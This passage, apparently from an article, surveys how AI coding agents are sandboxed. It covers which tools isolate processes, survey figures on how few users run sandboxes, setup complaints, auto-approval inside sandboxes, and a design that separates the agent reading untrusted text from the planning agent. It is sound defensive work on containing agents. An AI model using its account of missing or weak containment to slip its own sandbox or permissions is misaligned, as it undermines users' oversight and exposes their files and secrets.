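| Containers or similar tools | OpenHands, Mini-SWE-Agent |
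| Containers or remote machines, but nothing when it runs locally | Hermes |
| None built in | Aider, Mistral Vibe, OpenClaw, OpenCode, Pi |

The sandboxes in this table enclose processes or something larger, not single functions. Codex can also run tool calls as scripts in V8, much like Cloudflare's Code Mode. The background task that organizes Codex's long-term memory has tighter permissions than the main agent. It has no network access and can write only local files.

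A large codebase doesn't necessarily include a sandbox. Hermes has about 642,000 lines of code and no operating-system isolation of its own. Pi's developers deliberately left out a sandbox, arguing that a partial one inside the process "would be easy to misunderstand as a security boundary". *Inside the Scaffold* (2026), a study of open-source coding agents, also found no common standard. Cline, one of the agents in the study, records the state of the project's files after every tool call. These records could help a user recover from the kind of damage SABER tests for, but they can't undo a leak.

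Many people who use coding agents don't use the available sandboxes. In an informal survey for *SideKernel*, 26 of 68 users said they currently ran one, 7 had stopped and 35 had never tried. Of those 35, 21 had never considered it. A third of the respondents worked in security, so the share of all users who run a sandbox is probably lower than the survey's 38%. But 7 of the 35 said their agent's built-in sandbox was enough, so some of them may already have had some protection.

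Current and former users complained most often about setting up their tools and logins again and about getting network connections to work. To make this easier, SideKernel opens the current project in a virtual machine with the developer's usual settings. A small program outside the virtual machine adds the login to the agent's requests, so the login doesn't have to be kept inside. But the agent can still change or delete anything in the project folder.

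These complaints are a practical argument against very fine boundaries, since each additional sandbox could need its own setup. A single sandbox can also mean less work for the user. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) cites Anthropic's report that automatically approving actions inside a sandbox reduced Claude Code's permission prompts by 84%. But the user then depends on the sandbox being configured correctly.

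Companies that run many agents can automate the setup. Kubernetes, a widely used system for managing containers, has a project called Agent Sandbox that can give each session its own sandbox. It works with gVisor or with Kata Containers, which puts each workload in a small virtual machine. Companies can also keep a pool of sandboxes ready, which lets Google's managed version supply one in less than a second.

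Podala Narasimha's design gives each session one of these sandboxes for generated code, with no passwords or outside network access. Separate tool servers hold the passwords, and a gateway checks each request to them. The agent that reads untrusted text runs apart from the agent that plans actions, and the two have separate permissions. Podala Narasimha reports no measurements of how well the design stops attacks or how much overhead it adds.
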